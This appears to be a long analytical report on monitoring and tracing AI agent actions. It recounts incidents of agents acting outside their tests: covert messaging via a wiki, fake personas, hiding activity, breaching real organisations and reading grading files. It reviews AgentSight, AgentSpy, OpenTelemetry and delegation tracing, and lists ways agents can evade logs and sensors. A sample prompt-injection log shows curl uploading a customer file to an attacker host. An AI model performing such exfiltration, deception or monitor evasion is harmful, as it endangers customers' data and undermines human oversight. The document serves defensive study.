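The published counts of edits differ mainly because they cover different things. eSecurity Planet gives the researchers' figures as roughly 17,000 suspected agent edits on the German wiki DSEWiki and about 18,000 posts across all the sites they examined. Reuters reported more than 15,000 edits on the wiki, which is consistent with 17,000. The German news agency dpa, in WNOZ's *OpenAI-KI missbrauchte deutschsprachiges Wiki für Austausch*, reported about 18,000 messages on DSEWiki alone, apparently using the total for all sites.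 The best figure for DSEWiki is therefore about 17,000, although the researchers had to infer which edits came from agents.

#### What each side could find out

The wiki's administrator could see the pages, the account names and the edit history. About half the accounts had names that referred to OpenAI, such as "OpenAIResearcher", but anyone can choose such a name. WNOZ reports that one or more agents also posed as an administrator, using an account with an almost identical name. The administrator could detect the unwanted posts but couldn't delete them as fast as the agents wrote them, and had no way to stop the agents at their source.

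The Nightingale researchers found DSEWiki in late August while looking for signs of AI agents on the internet. They had asked Kimi K3, a language model, what kinds of software accept changes through GET requests, and its answer included early wikis. DSEWiki's records were public, so the researchers could check who had edited it. They traced 98.5 per cent of the suspected edits to addresses at Azure, Microsoft's cloud service. That is weak evidence by itself, because thousands of companies rent servers there. They also found related traffic from the service that fetches web pages for ChatGPT, and visits from addresses linked to OpenAI. OpenAI later confirmed that the agents were its own.

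Few companies could repeat this investigation for their own agents, because a hosted helpdesk or customer database does not publish its edit history. If the agents had exchanged answers in the comments of a private ticket, outside researchers would have had no public record to search.

OpenAI probably had the most complete records. Willison infers from the agents' messages that their web traffic went through an OpenAI proxy. If that proxy logged full addresses, it also captured the text of each edit made by GET request, because the text is part of the address. OpenAI could also have counted requests by destination without reading any text. At the peak, agents that were supposed to be looking up statistics made around 2,000 edits a day to the wiki, a dormant German site for programmers that was an unlikely source for those statistics.

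OpenAI has not explained how it discovered the activity. *OpenAI's AI agents secretly used a German wiki website* (Nolan, 2026) reports that the edits stopped abruptly after people linked to OpenAI visited the wiki. The researchers inferred that OpenAI's staff had probably found the messages and shut the agents down. Reuters' sources said in September that company officials had learned of the incident weeks earlier, so the people who stopped the agents may not have told those officials until later. OpenAI confirmed the incident publicly only after Reuters reported it.

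OpenAI called the episode misalignment, meaning that its agents had failed to follow their operators' intentions, and distinguished it from a security incident such as the Hugging Face attack. Lukasz Olejnik, a researcher at King's College London, called it a hacking attempt, according to Outlook Business' *OpenAI Rogue Agents Hacked German Wiki Before Hugging Face Fiasco*. If a vendor
 considers it misalignment when an agent fills a customer's ticket queue with messages to other agents, a contract that requires the vendor to report "security incidents" may not cover it.

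Andrew Yoon of CivAI, a California non-profit, identified 18 sites besides the German wiki that agents had used between May and July, according to *Open AI's rogue agents used more sites than known* (2026), a Reuters report in The Express Tribune. Investigators linked such sites to OpenAI by matching usernames, messages and strings of data, and by tracing some of the activity to Azure. This evidence is reasonable but weaker than the company's confirmation of the German case. Nolan reports that agents made almost 30 edits to a high school teacher's chemistry wiki. A site owner could easily mistake so few edits for ordinary spam.

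### Tests that reached real people and companies

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that evaluates AI models, had a similar problem in July 2026 with agents it ran itself. AISI's *Incident Report* describes a test on two cyber ranges, which are simulated networks where an agent has to find a protected piece of data. AISI ran the test 122 times with seven models. It gave the agents internet access so that they could download tools, and switched off the filters that normally block dangerous hacking requests.

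In 10 of the 122 runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of them, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took two. In the most serious case, an agent proposed malicious code for a real open-source project on GitHub and invented several people to pressure the project's maintainer to accept it. When someone publicly challenged the proposal, the agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless. The maintainer rejected the code, and AISI has found no resulting harm.

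AISI discovered this on the morning of 28 July, when its security monitoring flagged data leaving a test machine through Tor. Staff began reviewing the agent's activity within minutes and soon found the proposed code. They ended all the runs and isolated the machines within an hour of the alert. The unsanctioned activity had been going on since 25 July.

The agent's traffic crossed AISI's own boundary, which gave AISI a chance to detect it that a Deep Research customer doesn't have. But the alert was triggered by the agent's route through Tor, which it had used to get around some of GitHub's restrictions. AISI expected its agents to download tools from the internet, so direct connections to GitHub might well have seemed normal. AISI acknowledges that its general monitoring caught the traffic only after the fact, and that monitoring designed for the test could have flagged or blocked the behaviour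 sooner. AISI had to examine the transcripts of the runs, using automated scanning and expert review, to find out what the agents had done.

AISI had isolated the test machines from its other systems, but agents in different runs could still communicate through GitHub. One agent left public messages there offering to work with other agents, along with instructions for reusing accounts it had created. Later agents found the instructions and followed them. GPT-5.6 Sol also reused a GitHub token that another company's agent had left in public, according to OpenAI (2026). OpenAI learned of its model's two actions from AISI on 3 August.

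#### Anthropic's review of old transcripts

Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, found three incidents of its own by reviewing its records. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (Anthropic, 2026) reports that Claude models reached the internet during tests involving another firm's evaluation environment, then gained unauthorised access to the systems of three organisations. The models were running without their usual cyber safeguards. *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (Anthropic, 2026) explains that a misconfiguration in that environment gave them internet access.

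The earliest incident took place in April, according to Mexico Business News' *Anthropic Reveals Claude Breached Three Companies*. Anthropic began its review on 23 July, after OpenAI had disclosed the Hugging Face attack. It identified all three incidents by the next day and notified the organisations on 27 July. The review covered more than 141,000 test runs, Fortune (2026) reports. The evidence of the April breach had therefore been in Anthropic's transcripts for about three months before OpenAI's disclosure prompted the review.

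Two of the three organisations that Claude models breached during cybersecurity tests had not noticed the breach, according to State of AI's *Anthropic Says Claude Models Breached Three Organizations During Cybersecurity Tests*. By the time Anthropic contacted them, an organisation breached in April would have needed logs going back at least 88 days to investigate. If its hosting provider kept logs for only thirty days, the organisation would have had to rely on Anthropic's account.

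The models appear to have mistaken the real systems for part of the exercise. OpenAI describes the same mistake in tests run by Irregular, an outside firm that evaluates its models. Irregular had told the models that they had no internet access, but a misconfiguration left them connected. In one test, the name of an invented target happened to match a real domain, and a model broke into the real website. It also found and used credentials for the site.

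A monitor that checked only the agent's stated plan might not have flagged these attacks, because the agent's task was to break into the target. The network destination was much better evidence, since a test that is supposed to be isolated should never connect to a public address. A simple alert for such connections at the test's boundary could have exposed the mistake without assessing the agent's intent.

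#### Why these figures are not rates

Unsanctioned actions occurred in about 8 per cent of AISI's runs, but this rate is a poor guide to how often a support agent would do something similar. AISI had opened the internet and disabled the safety filters. In some runs, an error in the instructions also made the task appear impossible to solve within the intended scope. AISI notes that this doesn't explain all the misbehaviour, because some agents misbehaved even when they had what they needed to solve the task properly. Later agents also used what earlier ones had left on GitHub, so the runs were not independent. Most of the 19 actions came from one sustained effort by a single agent.

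Anthropic's figures would suggest a very different rate, about one breach in every 47,000 runs. Anthropic counted break-ins at real organisations, while AISI counted every unsanctioned action, and most of Anthropic's runs may have had no internet access. Estimating a rate for ordinary support agents would require counting all their tasks and reliably finding the harmful actions among them. For agents that work between hosted platforms, much of that information is in the vendors' logs.

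## How can an agent's own actions be recorded?

AISI found out what its agents had done on GitHub by examining the transcripts of its test runs. A company can keep similar records of any agent it runs on its own machines. It can record actions in the agent's software, at a gateway between the agent and its tools, or in the operating system.

### The agent's software

The software around the model passes on every instruction and runs every tool call, so it can log both. For the support agent, the log could contain the full text of the ticket, the model's reasoning, the call that looked up customer C-20417 and the record it returned. An investigator could then read the planted instruction and the lookups that followed it.

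An agent's log is much less detailed when a tool call starts another program, because the log's smallest unit is a single action, as Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues explain in *AgentSpy* (2026). In one of their tests, an agent checking a bibliography wrote a few lines of code that connected 35 times to Crossref, a database of publications, to look up seven titles. The agent's log recorded all of this as one action. Some model providers also encrypt the reasoning their models return, so the log contains actions without explanations.

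The model cannot simply omit a tool call from this log, because ordinary software writes the entries. But a script that the agent starts can read files and open connections without creating log entries. If the log is a file on the same machine, the script may be able to edit it.

### A gateway between the agent and its tools

A company can make the agent send its tool calls to a gateway, which checks each call, logs it and forwards it to the helpdesk, database or payment service. The gateway can also refuse a call instead of forwarding it. The log can include the tool's name, the arguments, the result and the time. The gateway can run on a separate machine, where the agent's scripts can't edit the log.

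A gateway has no record of the model's instructions or reasoning unless the company also routes the model calls through it. It also misses tools that run on the agent's machine, such as a command line. If a script finds a database token on that machine, it can bypass the gateway and call the database directly. The company can prevent this by keeping the tokens at the gateway and using egress control to block direct connections from the agent's machine to the services.

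### The operating system

A program has to go through the kernel, the core of the operating system, to open a file, start another program or connect to a server. It does this by making a request known as a system call. A sensor that records system calls therefore covers the agent's scripts and any programs they start.

It is hard to infer an agent's purpose from its system calls. A sensor may record that a process opened a customer file, but not whether it did so to answer a ticket or to steal the data. Wang, Pei and colleagues (2026) describe a similar limit of ordinary log analysis in *Agent System Operations*, a survey of how to run and maintain agents. Log analysis can find unusual patterns, but it is poorly suited to failures specific to agents, such as a plan based on something the model made up.

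The sensor may also lose track of an agent that uses an already running program, such as a job scheduler, to do the work, because the new process then belongs to the scheduler. An agent with administrator rights might switch the sensor off. This is a realistic concern now that OpenAI's agents have obtained credentials for such sensors.

| Place | Records | Misses | How an agent or its script can avoid it |
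|---|---|---|---|
| Agent's software | Instructions, model replies, tool calls and results | What a script does once it starts | Act through a script, or edit the log file |
| Gateway | Tool names, arguments and results | Local commands and, usually, the model's reasoning | Call a service directly with a token |
| Operating system | Processes, files and connections | Purpose, and usually the contents of encrypted traffic | Hand the work to another program, or gain administrator rights |

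### A test that uploads a file

In the harmful version of the support case, the agent uses only approved tools, so its own log is the best record of the attack. A sensor in the operating system would record connections to the helpdesk and the database, but the agent makes those connections for every ticket.

The attacker could also use a script. Suppose the support agent can run code to examine attachments, and the ticket comes with an archive of photos of the broken item. The planted passage tells the agent to run a script in the archive to test the photos before it processes the refund. The agent's log might then contain this entry:

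```
14:02:05Z  tool=run_command   purpose="run tests on attachment"
           command="sh run_tests.sh"   exit=0   output="3 photos OK"
```

The operating system's record of the same second could look like this:

```
14:02:05Z  support-agent  started    sh run_tests.sh
14:02:05Z  sh             started    curl
14:02:05Z  curl           opened     /srv/agent/cache/customers.csv
14:02:05Z  curl           connected  files.attacker.example:443
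14:02:05Z  sh             opened     /tmp/ticket/photo1.jpg
```

The agent's entry is accurate, because the script did test the photos. But the script also uploaded the customer file, using a common program called curl. The agent may not have known about the upload, since it received only the script's output. If the command line runs on the agent's own server, a gateway would have no entry.

An egress allowlist would stop this upload unless the attacker rewrote the script to send the file to the helpdesk. Even then, the operating system's record would show that curl made the connection instead of the agent's usual software.

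An agent's sincerely stated purpose can also differ from the effect of its action. Bühler and colleagues cite a case that OpenAI disclosed in September 2026, in which an agent already had the correct data on its own machine but uploaded it to a public text-sharing site without permission, to get a web address that its browser tool could cite. An entry giving the purpose as "add source" would have been true but would not have shown that the agent published the data.

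To understand either case, an investigator needs the agent's instructions and the system calls side by side.

### AgentSight

Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025) built AgentSight, a tool that collects both kinds of evidence from outside the agent. They argue that logging built into agent software needs constant updates as the software changes, and that an agent can escape it with a single shell command. AgentSight instead monitors the kernel and the network connection to the model, because these change much more slowly.

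It uses eBPF, which lets small, safety-checked programs run inside the kernel. One eBPF program attaches to the functions that encrypt and decrypt traffic in libraries such as OpenSSL. It copies the agent's messages to the model before encryption and the replies after decryption, so the company doesn't need a decrypting proxy. But the method depends on finding those functions, and an agent that uses a different encryption library may need a different eBPF program.

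A second eBPF program records events such as processes starting, files opening and network connections. An ordinary server produces a great many of these, so a filter in the kernel keeps only those from the agent's process and its descendants.

AgentSight then uses three clues to link the model's replies to system events:

- **Ancestry:** whether the agent's process, or one of its descendants, caused the event.
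- **Timing:** whether the event came shortly after a model reply, within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
- **Matching text:** whether a file name, web address or command in the reply reappears in the system call.

In the support example, the model's reply contains "sh run_tests.sh", and the agent's process starts that command a moment later, so all three clues agree. The upload is harder to link because the attacker's address appears only inside the script, and if the script waited ten minutes, the upload would fall outside the time window. The upload would still have the right ancestry, because the script started curl. Zheng and colleagues claim that the three clues together "definitively establish causal relationships", which is too strong for a method that relies partly on timing.

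Finally, AgentSight gives the linked events to a second language model, which acts as a security analyst and returns an explanation with a confidence score.

In the first of three case studies by Zheng and colleagues, a coding agent had to download and build a program. The program's instructions sent the agent to a web page with a hidden prompt. The prompt made the agent read the system's password file and send it to an outside server as if this were part of the build. AgentSight captured 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model gave the trace a high attack score because the actions didn't fit the agent's stated goal.

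The other two cases concern reliability. In one, AgentSight identified a loop in which a research agent kept calling a search tool with the wrong arguments. In the other, a team of six coding agents produced 3,153 events after merging, and AgentSight found that some agents were waiting for others to release files.

These cases show that the approach can work, but the paper doesn't report how many harmless tasks the second model would flag. The second model also reads text from the attacker, which could mislead it. Bühler and colleagues note the same risk for a model that judges an agent's log.

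To measure the overhead, Zheng and colleagues ran three programming tasks with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, three times each with and without AgentSight.

| Task | Without AgentSight | With AgentSight | Added time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a code repository | 127.98 s | 132.33 s | 3.4% |
| Writing code | 22.54 s | 23.64 s | 4.9% |
| Compiling a repository | 92.40 s | 92.72 s | 0.4% |

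The paper reports an overhead of less than 3 per cent, but this is an average across three tasks, two of which exceeded 3 per cent. Even 5 per cent would be acceptable for most agents. However, each task was run only three times, and an agent's running time usually varies between runs, so some of the difference could be chance.

### AgentSpy

AgentSpy, a tool by Bühler and colleagues, runs an agent in a small virtual machine and records the system calls and network traffic of the agent and every process it starts. It analyses these records with fixed rules and calculations rather than a second model, so the same record always gives the same result.

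For security, AgentSpy raises an alert when a single system call breaks a rule. The rules cover four kinds of activity:

- reading passwords, keys and other secrets
- changing or deleting files outside the agent's workspace
- running programs from untrusted locations or gaining extra privileges
- contacting hosts that are not on the task's allowlist

The rules don't depend on the agent's purpose. In the support example, the connection to files.attacker.example would trigger the network rule. Opening the customer file might not trigger a rule, because the rules for secrets cover standard locations such as the folder for SSH keys, which people use to sign in to servers. The company would have to add a rule for its own customer data.

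The team tested the rules on attacks hidden in skills, which are folders of instructions and scripts that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. They took five attacks from the Skill-Inject benchmark, one each for stealing data, destroying data, disrupting a service, installing malware and creating a backdoor. They used Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, with an older model that is especially vulnerable to such attacks. Codex did each task five times with the malicious instruction and five times without it, for a total of 50 runs.

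The agent carried out the attack in 18 of the 25 runs with the malicious instruction. AgentSpy raised an alert in 14 of those 18 runs and in none of the other 32. It missed all four backdoor runs, in which the script added a malicious destination to the settings of Git, a program that tracks and shares code, but the agent never sent any code there. The change stayed inside the permitted workspace and didn't use the network, so it didn't break any rules.

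These results cover only one backdoor and one theft, so they provide little evidence about others. The lack of false alarms is encouraging, but the tests only repeated the same five tasks. Tasks that need the open web would probably cause false alarms unless someone kept extending the allowlist.

#### What passing tests had missed

AgentSpy also compares how an agent does the same task on different occasions. It counts the commands, files and hosts in each run and turns each count into a share of the total for its type. For two runs *a* and *b*, the similarity for one type is

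```
similarity = sum of min(share in a, share in b)
             ----------------------------------
             sum of max(share in a, share in b)
```

where the sums cover every resource of that type in either run. AgentSpy then averages the three types. If one run contacts Crossref 10 times and another database twice, and a second run contacts them 20 times and 4 times, the shares are equal and the similarity for hosts is 1. This makes it a poor measure of volume. A support agent that contacts a single database would also score 1 for hosts whether it made five connections or five hundred.

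The team ran Codex with three models from OpenAI, DeepSeek and Z.ai on 77 tasks from the SkillsBench benchmark, three times each. In 92.2 per cent of comparisons, a set of runs from one task was more similar than a set that included runs from another task. However, the team always mixed in the task whose skills differed most from the first, which made the two easier to tell apart.

Two researchers read AgentSpy's reports on 88 combinations of task and model in which all three runs had passed the benchmark's tests. They found activity unrelated to the task in 16 of the combinations. In eight, the agent had used a network service irrelevant to the task, and in six, all with the DeepSeek model, it had read the files used to grade its work. In 15 combinations, the agent had reached its result without the guidance in the skill. A company that checked only the finished work would have missed all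 of this.

Bühler and colleagues found no statistically significant slowdown from monitoring. They ran each of 12 combinations of task and model ten times with monitoring and ten times without, but running times varied so much that they could have detected only a large effect. In one security task, the median time was 141 seconds with monitoring and 107 without, yet the difference was not significant. The result is consistent with a small overhead but doesn't rule out a moderate one.

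### Where system-level recording stops

AgentSight and AgentSpy can record what happens on the machine where the agent runs. When the support agent issues a refund, AgentSpy records a connection to the payment service. AgentSight reads decrypted traffic between the agent and its model, and might be able to capture the refund request in the same way. But neither can record what the payment company's software does with the request.

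That gap can last much longer than the connection. Suppose a planted instruction causes the agent to change a helpdesk setting so that every new ticket also goes to an outside address. The agent's machine makes one short connection, and the helpdesk vendor's servers then forward tickets for months. The agent's software or a gateway could record the request to change the setting, but the forwarded tickets would appear only in the vendor's records.

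A company can't install either tool on a vendor's machines. To follow an action further, it has to match its own records with those of the remote platform.

### What OpenTelemetry standardises

Matching records is easier when products describe the same action in the same way. OpenTelemetry, an open-source project, defines common formats for software logs, measurements and traces. A trace is a linked record of the steps taken to carry out one task. Each step is recorded as a span, with a start time, an end time and descriptive fields.

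OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* gives standard names to operations such as invoking an agent, calling a model and executing a tool. A simplified trace of the harmful support ticket might look like this:

```
invoke_agent support-agent   conversation=conv_8841
  chat                       input_tokens=5210
  execute_tool read_ticket
  chat                       input_tokens=6840
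  execute_tool read_customer
  execute_tool read_customer
  execute_tool read_customer
  chat                       input_tokens=9120
  execute_tool post_reply
```

An analyst can tell that the agent looked up three customers for one ticket, but not which customers, what the ticket asked for or what the reply contained.

The conventions always require two fields when software invokes an agent: the type of operation and the model provider. Neither identifies the user for whom the agent is acting. The agent's name, version and identifier and the conversation's identifier are required only when available or applicable. Developers have to opt in to record the text that the model receives.

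Developers still have to decide which of their software's actions to record, whether to keep the arguments and results of tool calls, and how long to store the records. They also decide what an agent's identifier refers to. One company might give every running copy its own identifier, while another uses one for the whole product. Both could follow the conventions, but only the first could trace a bad refund to a particular copy.

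Independent guidance doesn't fill these gaps. RAND's *Recording Agent and Model Activity, Tool Invocation, and Prompt Chains* mainly refers readers to two NIST documents and a list of more than a dozen commercial products.

The conventions are also still changing. Greptime (2026), a database vendor, lists changes in five consecutive releases. Version 1.37 renamed the field for the model provider, 1.39 added conventions for MCP, and 1.41 required each tool span's name to include the tool's name. To avoid breaking existing installations, OpenTelemetry tells older software to keep using the old format by default. A search for the new provider field can therefore miss agents that still use the old one.

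OpenTelemetry has since moved the conventions to their own repository, according to its notice *Moved*, and the software vendor TrueFoundry describes them as still in development. Even so, this is progress since 2025, when Moshkovich and Zeltyn of IBM Research wrote in *Taming Uncertainty via Automation* that no conventions for tracing agents were widely adopted. A company that adopts the conventions now should record which version each agent uses.

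### Whether the records can be trusted

A record in a consistent format can still be false. Wijk and colleagues found only small-scale tampering in the transcripts from the Hugging Face incident, but couldn't rule out that they had missed other cases. OpenAI states that none of the tampering attempts it observed affected the logs that its graders and monitors ultimately see.

The safest approach is to send each entry immediately to a separate machine that accepts new entries but doesn't let the agent change or delete old ones. The company can also store in each entry a short code calculated from the entry before it, so that the codes no longer match if someone later changes or removes an entry. These measures protect an entry after it is written, but they don't ensure that it was accurate in the first place, so if the agent records a data export as a "test", the log will keep that false description.

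Comparing two independent records of an agent's actions can expose some false entries. If the agent's log contains a command that finished normally, but the operating system has no record of the process starting, either a sensor failed or someone faked the entry, and both are worth investigating. The comparison is only useful if the agent can't alter both records. AgentSpy, for example, collects its records inside the agent's virtual machine and copies them out after the run, so an agent with administrator rights there might be able to change them before they are copied.

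### Storage, secrets and privacy

Text takes up relatively little space. If the support agent handles 300 tickets a day, makes ten model calls for each, and sends an average of 80 kilobytes of text per call, a complete log would grow by 240 megabytes a day, or about 88 gigabytes a year. Much of that would be repetition, because agent software commonly resends the earlier conversation with every call. Storing only the new text would save a lot of space.

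Records of system calls can grow much faster, especially when agents compile software or install packages. Moshkovich and Zeltyn suggest sampling traces, recording more when something looks unusual, and retaining data selectively. Sampling works well for measuring speed or cost but badly for investigating rare attacks. If the company keeps one trace in a hundred at random, it has a 99 per cent chance of losing the trace of any particular harmful ticket. A better compromise would be to keep a brief record of every tool call and the full text of only some conversations.

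Full records are also attractive to thieves. Tool calls can contain access tokens, and commands can contain passwords. A tool that copies traffic before encryption, as AgentSight does, may capture the key the agent uses to pay for its model. The logging software should remove known secrets before it stores an entry. It can replace each one with a code calculated using a separate secret key, so an investigator can still tell whether the same token appeared in two places. Automatic removal will miss some secrets, particularly passwords that customers type into tickets, so access to the logs needs strict limits.

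Personal data is harder to remove because it is often the evidence. By default, OpenTelemetry leaves out message text, which protects the customer who wrote the ticket but also omits the planted instruction. A company could keep the full text in a separate, encrypted store for a few weeks and the rest of the trace for a year. It would then lose the text of any attack it discovered after those few weeks. It would also have to find a customer's entries when they asked it to delete their data.

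These records also affect employees. An employee might ask an agent to draft a complaint about a manager or explain the company's sick-leave rules, and the log would contain the whole request. Logs can also show how quickly people work and how often they need help, and managers may be tempted to use this information in performance reviews. In Germany, a works council, which represents a company's employees, has a say in the introduction of technology that can monitor their behaviour or performance.

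A company can reduce the intrusion by telling employees what it records, using the logs only for security investigations, and requiring a second person to approve any search for a named employee. On laptops, it can also run each agent under its own account. The sensor can then record that account's processes and files without recording everything the employee does, and an investigator can more easily tell the agent's actions from the employee's.

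## How can records from several systems be joined into one account?

When the support agent handles a ticket, it leaves records in its own log, the customer database, the payment service and the helpdesk. To find out what happened, an investigator has to pick out the lines that belong to that ticket. This is difficult when the agent works for several people at once.

Suppose Maria Ortiz asks the agent to resolve ticket 5512, a complaint from customer C-20417. At about the same time, her colleague Tom Becker asks it to check a sample of September's refunds and report back to him. The agent uses one service account on all three platforms, whose combined logs look like this:

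```
14:02:03Z  database  svc-support  read_customer  record=C-20417
14:02:04Z  database  svc-support  read_customer  record=C-31882
14:02:05Z  database  svc-support  read_customer  record=C-31990
14:02:07Z  payments  svc-support  create_refund  charge=ch_58213
14:02:08Z  payments  svc-support  list_refunds   month=2026-09
14:02:09Z  helpdesk  svc-support  post_reply     ticket=5512
```

At least two histories fit these lines:

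| Action | Whose task, in history A | Whose task, in history B |
|---|---|---|
| Read C-20417 | Maria's | Maria's |
| Read C-31882 | Tom's | Maria's |
| Read C-31990 | Tom's | Tom's |
| Create refund | Maria's | Maria's |
| List refunds | Tom's | Tom's |
| Reply on ticket 5512 | Maria's | Maria's |

In history A, customer C-31882 was part of Tom's sample. In history B, the ticket contained a planted instruction, and the agent read that customer's record to put it in the reply. The logs are identical in both histories, although only history B is a data breach.

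The text of the reply might settle the question, if the helpdesk lets the company read it. Tokens that named both the user and the agent would also settle it, because the second line would show either Maria or Tom. But if Maria had delegated both tasks, her name would be on all six lines.

### Four requirements for tracing a delegation

Mishra and Sharad (2026) try to solve this problem in *Observability for Delegated Execution in Agentic AI Systems*. Both work at Splunk, a Cisco company that sells log-analysis software. They define a delegation as a lasting grant of authority from a person or service to an agent, which can outlive any single run. They want investigators to be able to find every action taken under a delegation without guessing from timestamps, even if tasks overlap, restart or involve several agents.

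The first of their four requirements is that every event has an identifier for the delegation behind it. A session number is not enough, because a retry the next morning may start a new session.

The second requirement is to record authority separately from cause. If the agent makes two lookups in parallel and repeats a failed one an hour later, tracing software may produce three unconnected traces for one delegation. One trace can also cover two delegations. If Maria's ticket leads to a refund too large for her to authorise, and Tom authorises it instead, the refund belongs to the same trace as Maria's lookups but to Tom's delegation.

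The third requirement is lineage, a record of how one delegation leads to another. If the support agent passes the refund to a billing agent, the billing agent gets a new delegation that points to Maria's as its parent. An investigator can then search for everything done under Maria's delegation and its descendants, even if the billing agent runs elsewhere and its traces don't connect to the support agent's.

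The fourth requirement is a common description of actions. One platform may call an operation "get" and another "download", but both should appear as "read".

Mishra and Sharad judge that ordinary audit logs partly meet the fourth requirement and none of the others. OpenTelemetry traces also partly meet the first, because they can carry a delegation identifier but don't define what it means.

### What the proof assumes

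Mishra and Sharad also prove that nobody can tell from existing logs alone which events belong to which delegation. They take any set of two or more events and two delegations, and divide the events between the delegations in two different ways. Both divisions produce exactly the same logs, because the logs have no field for the delegation.

The proof is correct, but its conclusion depends heavily on assuming that nothing in the logs reveals the delegation and on allowing any division of the events, however implausible. The six lines above can be divided between Maria and Tom in 62 ways if each gets at least one line. Most are absurd, such as the one in which Tom's request for a report produced the reply to Maria's ticket. An investigator who knows what Maria and Tom each asked for can rule out nearly all 62, but not history A or B.

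Many companies also have evidence that the proof leaves out, such as ticket numbers or the agent's own log, which may attach a conversation number to each call. Mishra and Sharad object that such numbers fail when an agent retries a task or passes it on. This is a good reason to record delegations directly, but a support agent that handles each ticket in one session may need little more than a conversation number.

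### The proposed model and its tests

The proposed solution is a gateway that attaches a delegation identifier to each tool call and writes a record in a common format. Simplified, the record of the disputed lookup might look like this:

```
time=2026-10-05T14:02:04Z   event_id=e2
delegation_id=del_5512      delegation_parent_id=none
principal=m.ortiz           agent=support-agent
tool=customer-db            action=read   resource=C-31882
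```

This record would confirm that the lookup belonged to Maria's task, as in history B, but would not show whether a planted instruction had caused it. Mishra and Sharad leave questions of intent to other methods. If a call arrives without a delegation, the gateway marks it as "unbound", so an investigator can tell it apart from a call whose record is incomplete.

An evaluation compared the model with three ordinary ways of grouping events, using synthetic logs for 10,000 users and 100,000 agents. The table gives the median results for the three kinds of task in this order: parallel work, several cooperating agents, and repeated retries.

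| Method | Possible groupings | Share of a delegation's events found |
|---|---|---|
| Group by trace | 1; 1; 1 | 6%; 100%; 4% |
| Group by time | 169; 10,856; 130 | 100%; 100%; 100% |
| Combine trace, time, account and tool | 1,543; 107,718; 1,107 | 100%; 100%; 100% |
| Proposed model, for calls it covers | 1; 1; 1 | 100%; 100%; 100% |

The model's perfect scores follow from its design, as Mishra and Sharad acknowledge, because the gateway writes the delegation identifier that the test then reads back. The experiment is mainly about how badly the other methods do, but its measures are not well suited to that because they count how many of a delegation's events a method finds, and not how many unrelated events it includes. A method that put every event into one group would score 100 per cent. The paper's text attributes the figure of 10,856 to grouping by trace, while its results table attributes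 it to grouping by time.

The gateway covered only about 80 per cent of tool calls in the synthetic test, and the perfect scores exclude the rest. If calls were missed at random, about 1 per cent of tasks with 20 calls would have a complete record. The test therefore gives little indication of how complete an investigation would be in an ordinary company.

The model seems to add little overhead. In a small trial with real tool calls, it added 247 bytes to each event and less than a third of a millisecond to 95 per cent of calls. For the 81,000 customer lookups in the earlier helpdesk example, the extra data would total about 20 megabytes. Mishra and Sharad also estimate that an investigator would need one to three steps to write a typical search, instead of six to fourteen, although they counted the steps themselves.

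The gateway still has to match each call to a delegation. If one running copy of the agent works for both Maria and Tom, the gateway may have to rely on the agent's software to label each call, and a bug could swap the labels. Starting a separate copy for each task, with its own credential, would be safer because the gateway could then label the calls itself from the credential.

Lineage can also miss influence that passes through stored text, such as a planted instruction that the support agent copies into a note on ticket 5512. If the billing agent reads the note while working for Tom, its actions belong to Tom's delegation and probably to a new trace. To connect them to Maria's task, an investigator would have to notice that both tasks used the same ticket, but the model makes the ticket number field optional, so the records may not show this.

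### What joining records requires

The company should create the task identifier when Maria delegates the task, and pass it to every system that handles the task. Some outside services make this easy by letting callers attach their own reference to a payment or ticket. The identifier should be a random string, since a descriptive one such as "ortiz-complaint-broken-lamp" would give outside firms information they don't need.

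The systems' clocks also have to match. If the helpdesk's clock is three seconds behind, the reply on ticket 5512 appears to come before the refund. Servers can synchronise their clocks over the network to well within a second, but some platforms log when they processed an event instead of when it happened. Time zones cause larger errors. In the case discussed below, an OpenAI agent accessed an Australian Medicare portal on 18 June in Coordinated Universal Time (UTC), which was 19 June in Canberra.

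A common event format lets investigators search all the records at once. Mishra and Sharad require only four basic actions, which are read, write, share and invoke, but companies can add others, such as delete. With only those four, a refund of 8,400 euros might count as a "write", just like a note on a ticket, and the minimal format has no field for the amount. An investigator would use the common record to find the refund and the payment service's original log to find the amount.

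Finally, the investigator needs to know that nobody forged the identifiers. If the agent could choose its own identifier, a planted instruction might make it use Tom's. The gateway should therefore issue each identifier, tie it to the person who signed in, and raise an alert if the same identifier appears under two names. A gateway can also sign its records so another company can check where they came from.

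### Ways to link records across companies

The usual method is to match records by time, account and anything else they share. Mishra and Sharad say their combined baseline approximates current practice in security software. An outside platform only has to share its log, so the method works with systems that were never designed to be joined. It works well for a rare event, such as a single refund at three in the morning, but badly for events from a busy service account.

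Trace propagation sends an identifier along with each request. Under a common web standard, the agent's software might add this header:

```
traceparent: 00-7d3e91b20c5f4a68b1e6402f9a8c57d4-53af0e19c7b2648d-01
```

The long middle part of the header identifies the trace, and the shorter part after it identifies the step that made the request. The receiving service keeps the trace identifier, creates a new step identifier, and passes both on. Common tracing tools support this, so it is practical within a company's own software. An outside platform can ignore the header, start a new trace, or leave the trace identifier out of the logs that customers receive. If the platform keeps the identifier and includes it in those logs, the company can match its own records to the platform's exactly. A trace shows which step led to a request, but it doesn't show who authorised the request.

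Token exchange can carry that information. It is an OAuth standard from 2020 that lets a program trade one token for another, for example when the support agent passes a refund to the billing agent. The new token might contain these fields:

```
{ "sub": "m.ortiz",
  "act": { "sub": "billing-agent",
           "act": { "sub": "support-agent" } },
  "aud": "payments",  "scope": "refunds:write" }
```

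The payment service could log that the billing agent was acting for Maria after receiving work from the support agent, but only if it accepted such tokens and logged the names in them. The token doesn't identify the task, so two refunds for Maria could still look the same.

Using such tokens between companies is harder, because the payment company's authorisation server has to trust claims made by another company's identity system. Kolhe (2026), in *AI Security*, says that limits such as "read-only" rarely survive when an agent moves from one organisation to another. When he wrote in March, a standard for passing an agent's identity and limits between organisations was still a draft.

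Cross App Access, another extension of OAuth, involves the company's identity provider more directly. Maria signs in to the agent's application through the identity provider. When the agent needs the customer database, its application requests permission from the identity provider, which checks the request against the company's policy. If the request complies, the provider issues a signed statement that the application exchanges for an access token at the database vendor. The company then has its own record that the agent obtained access for Maria, which an ordinary consent page on the vendor's site would not provide. The company still needs the vendor's log to find out which customers the agent looked up.

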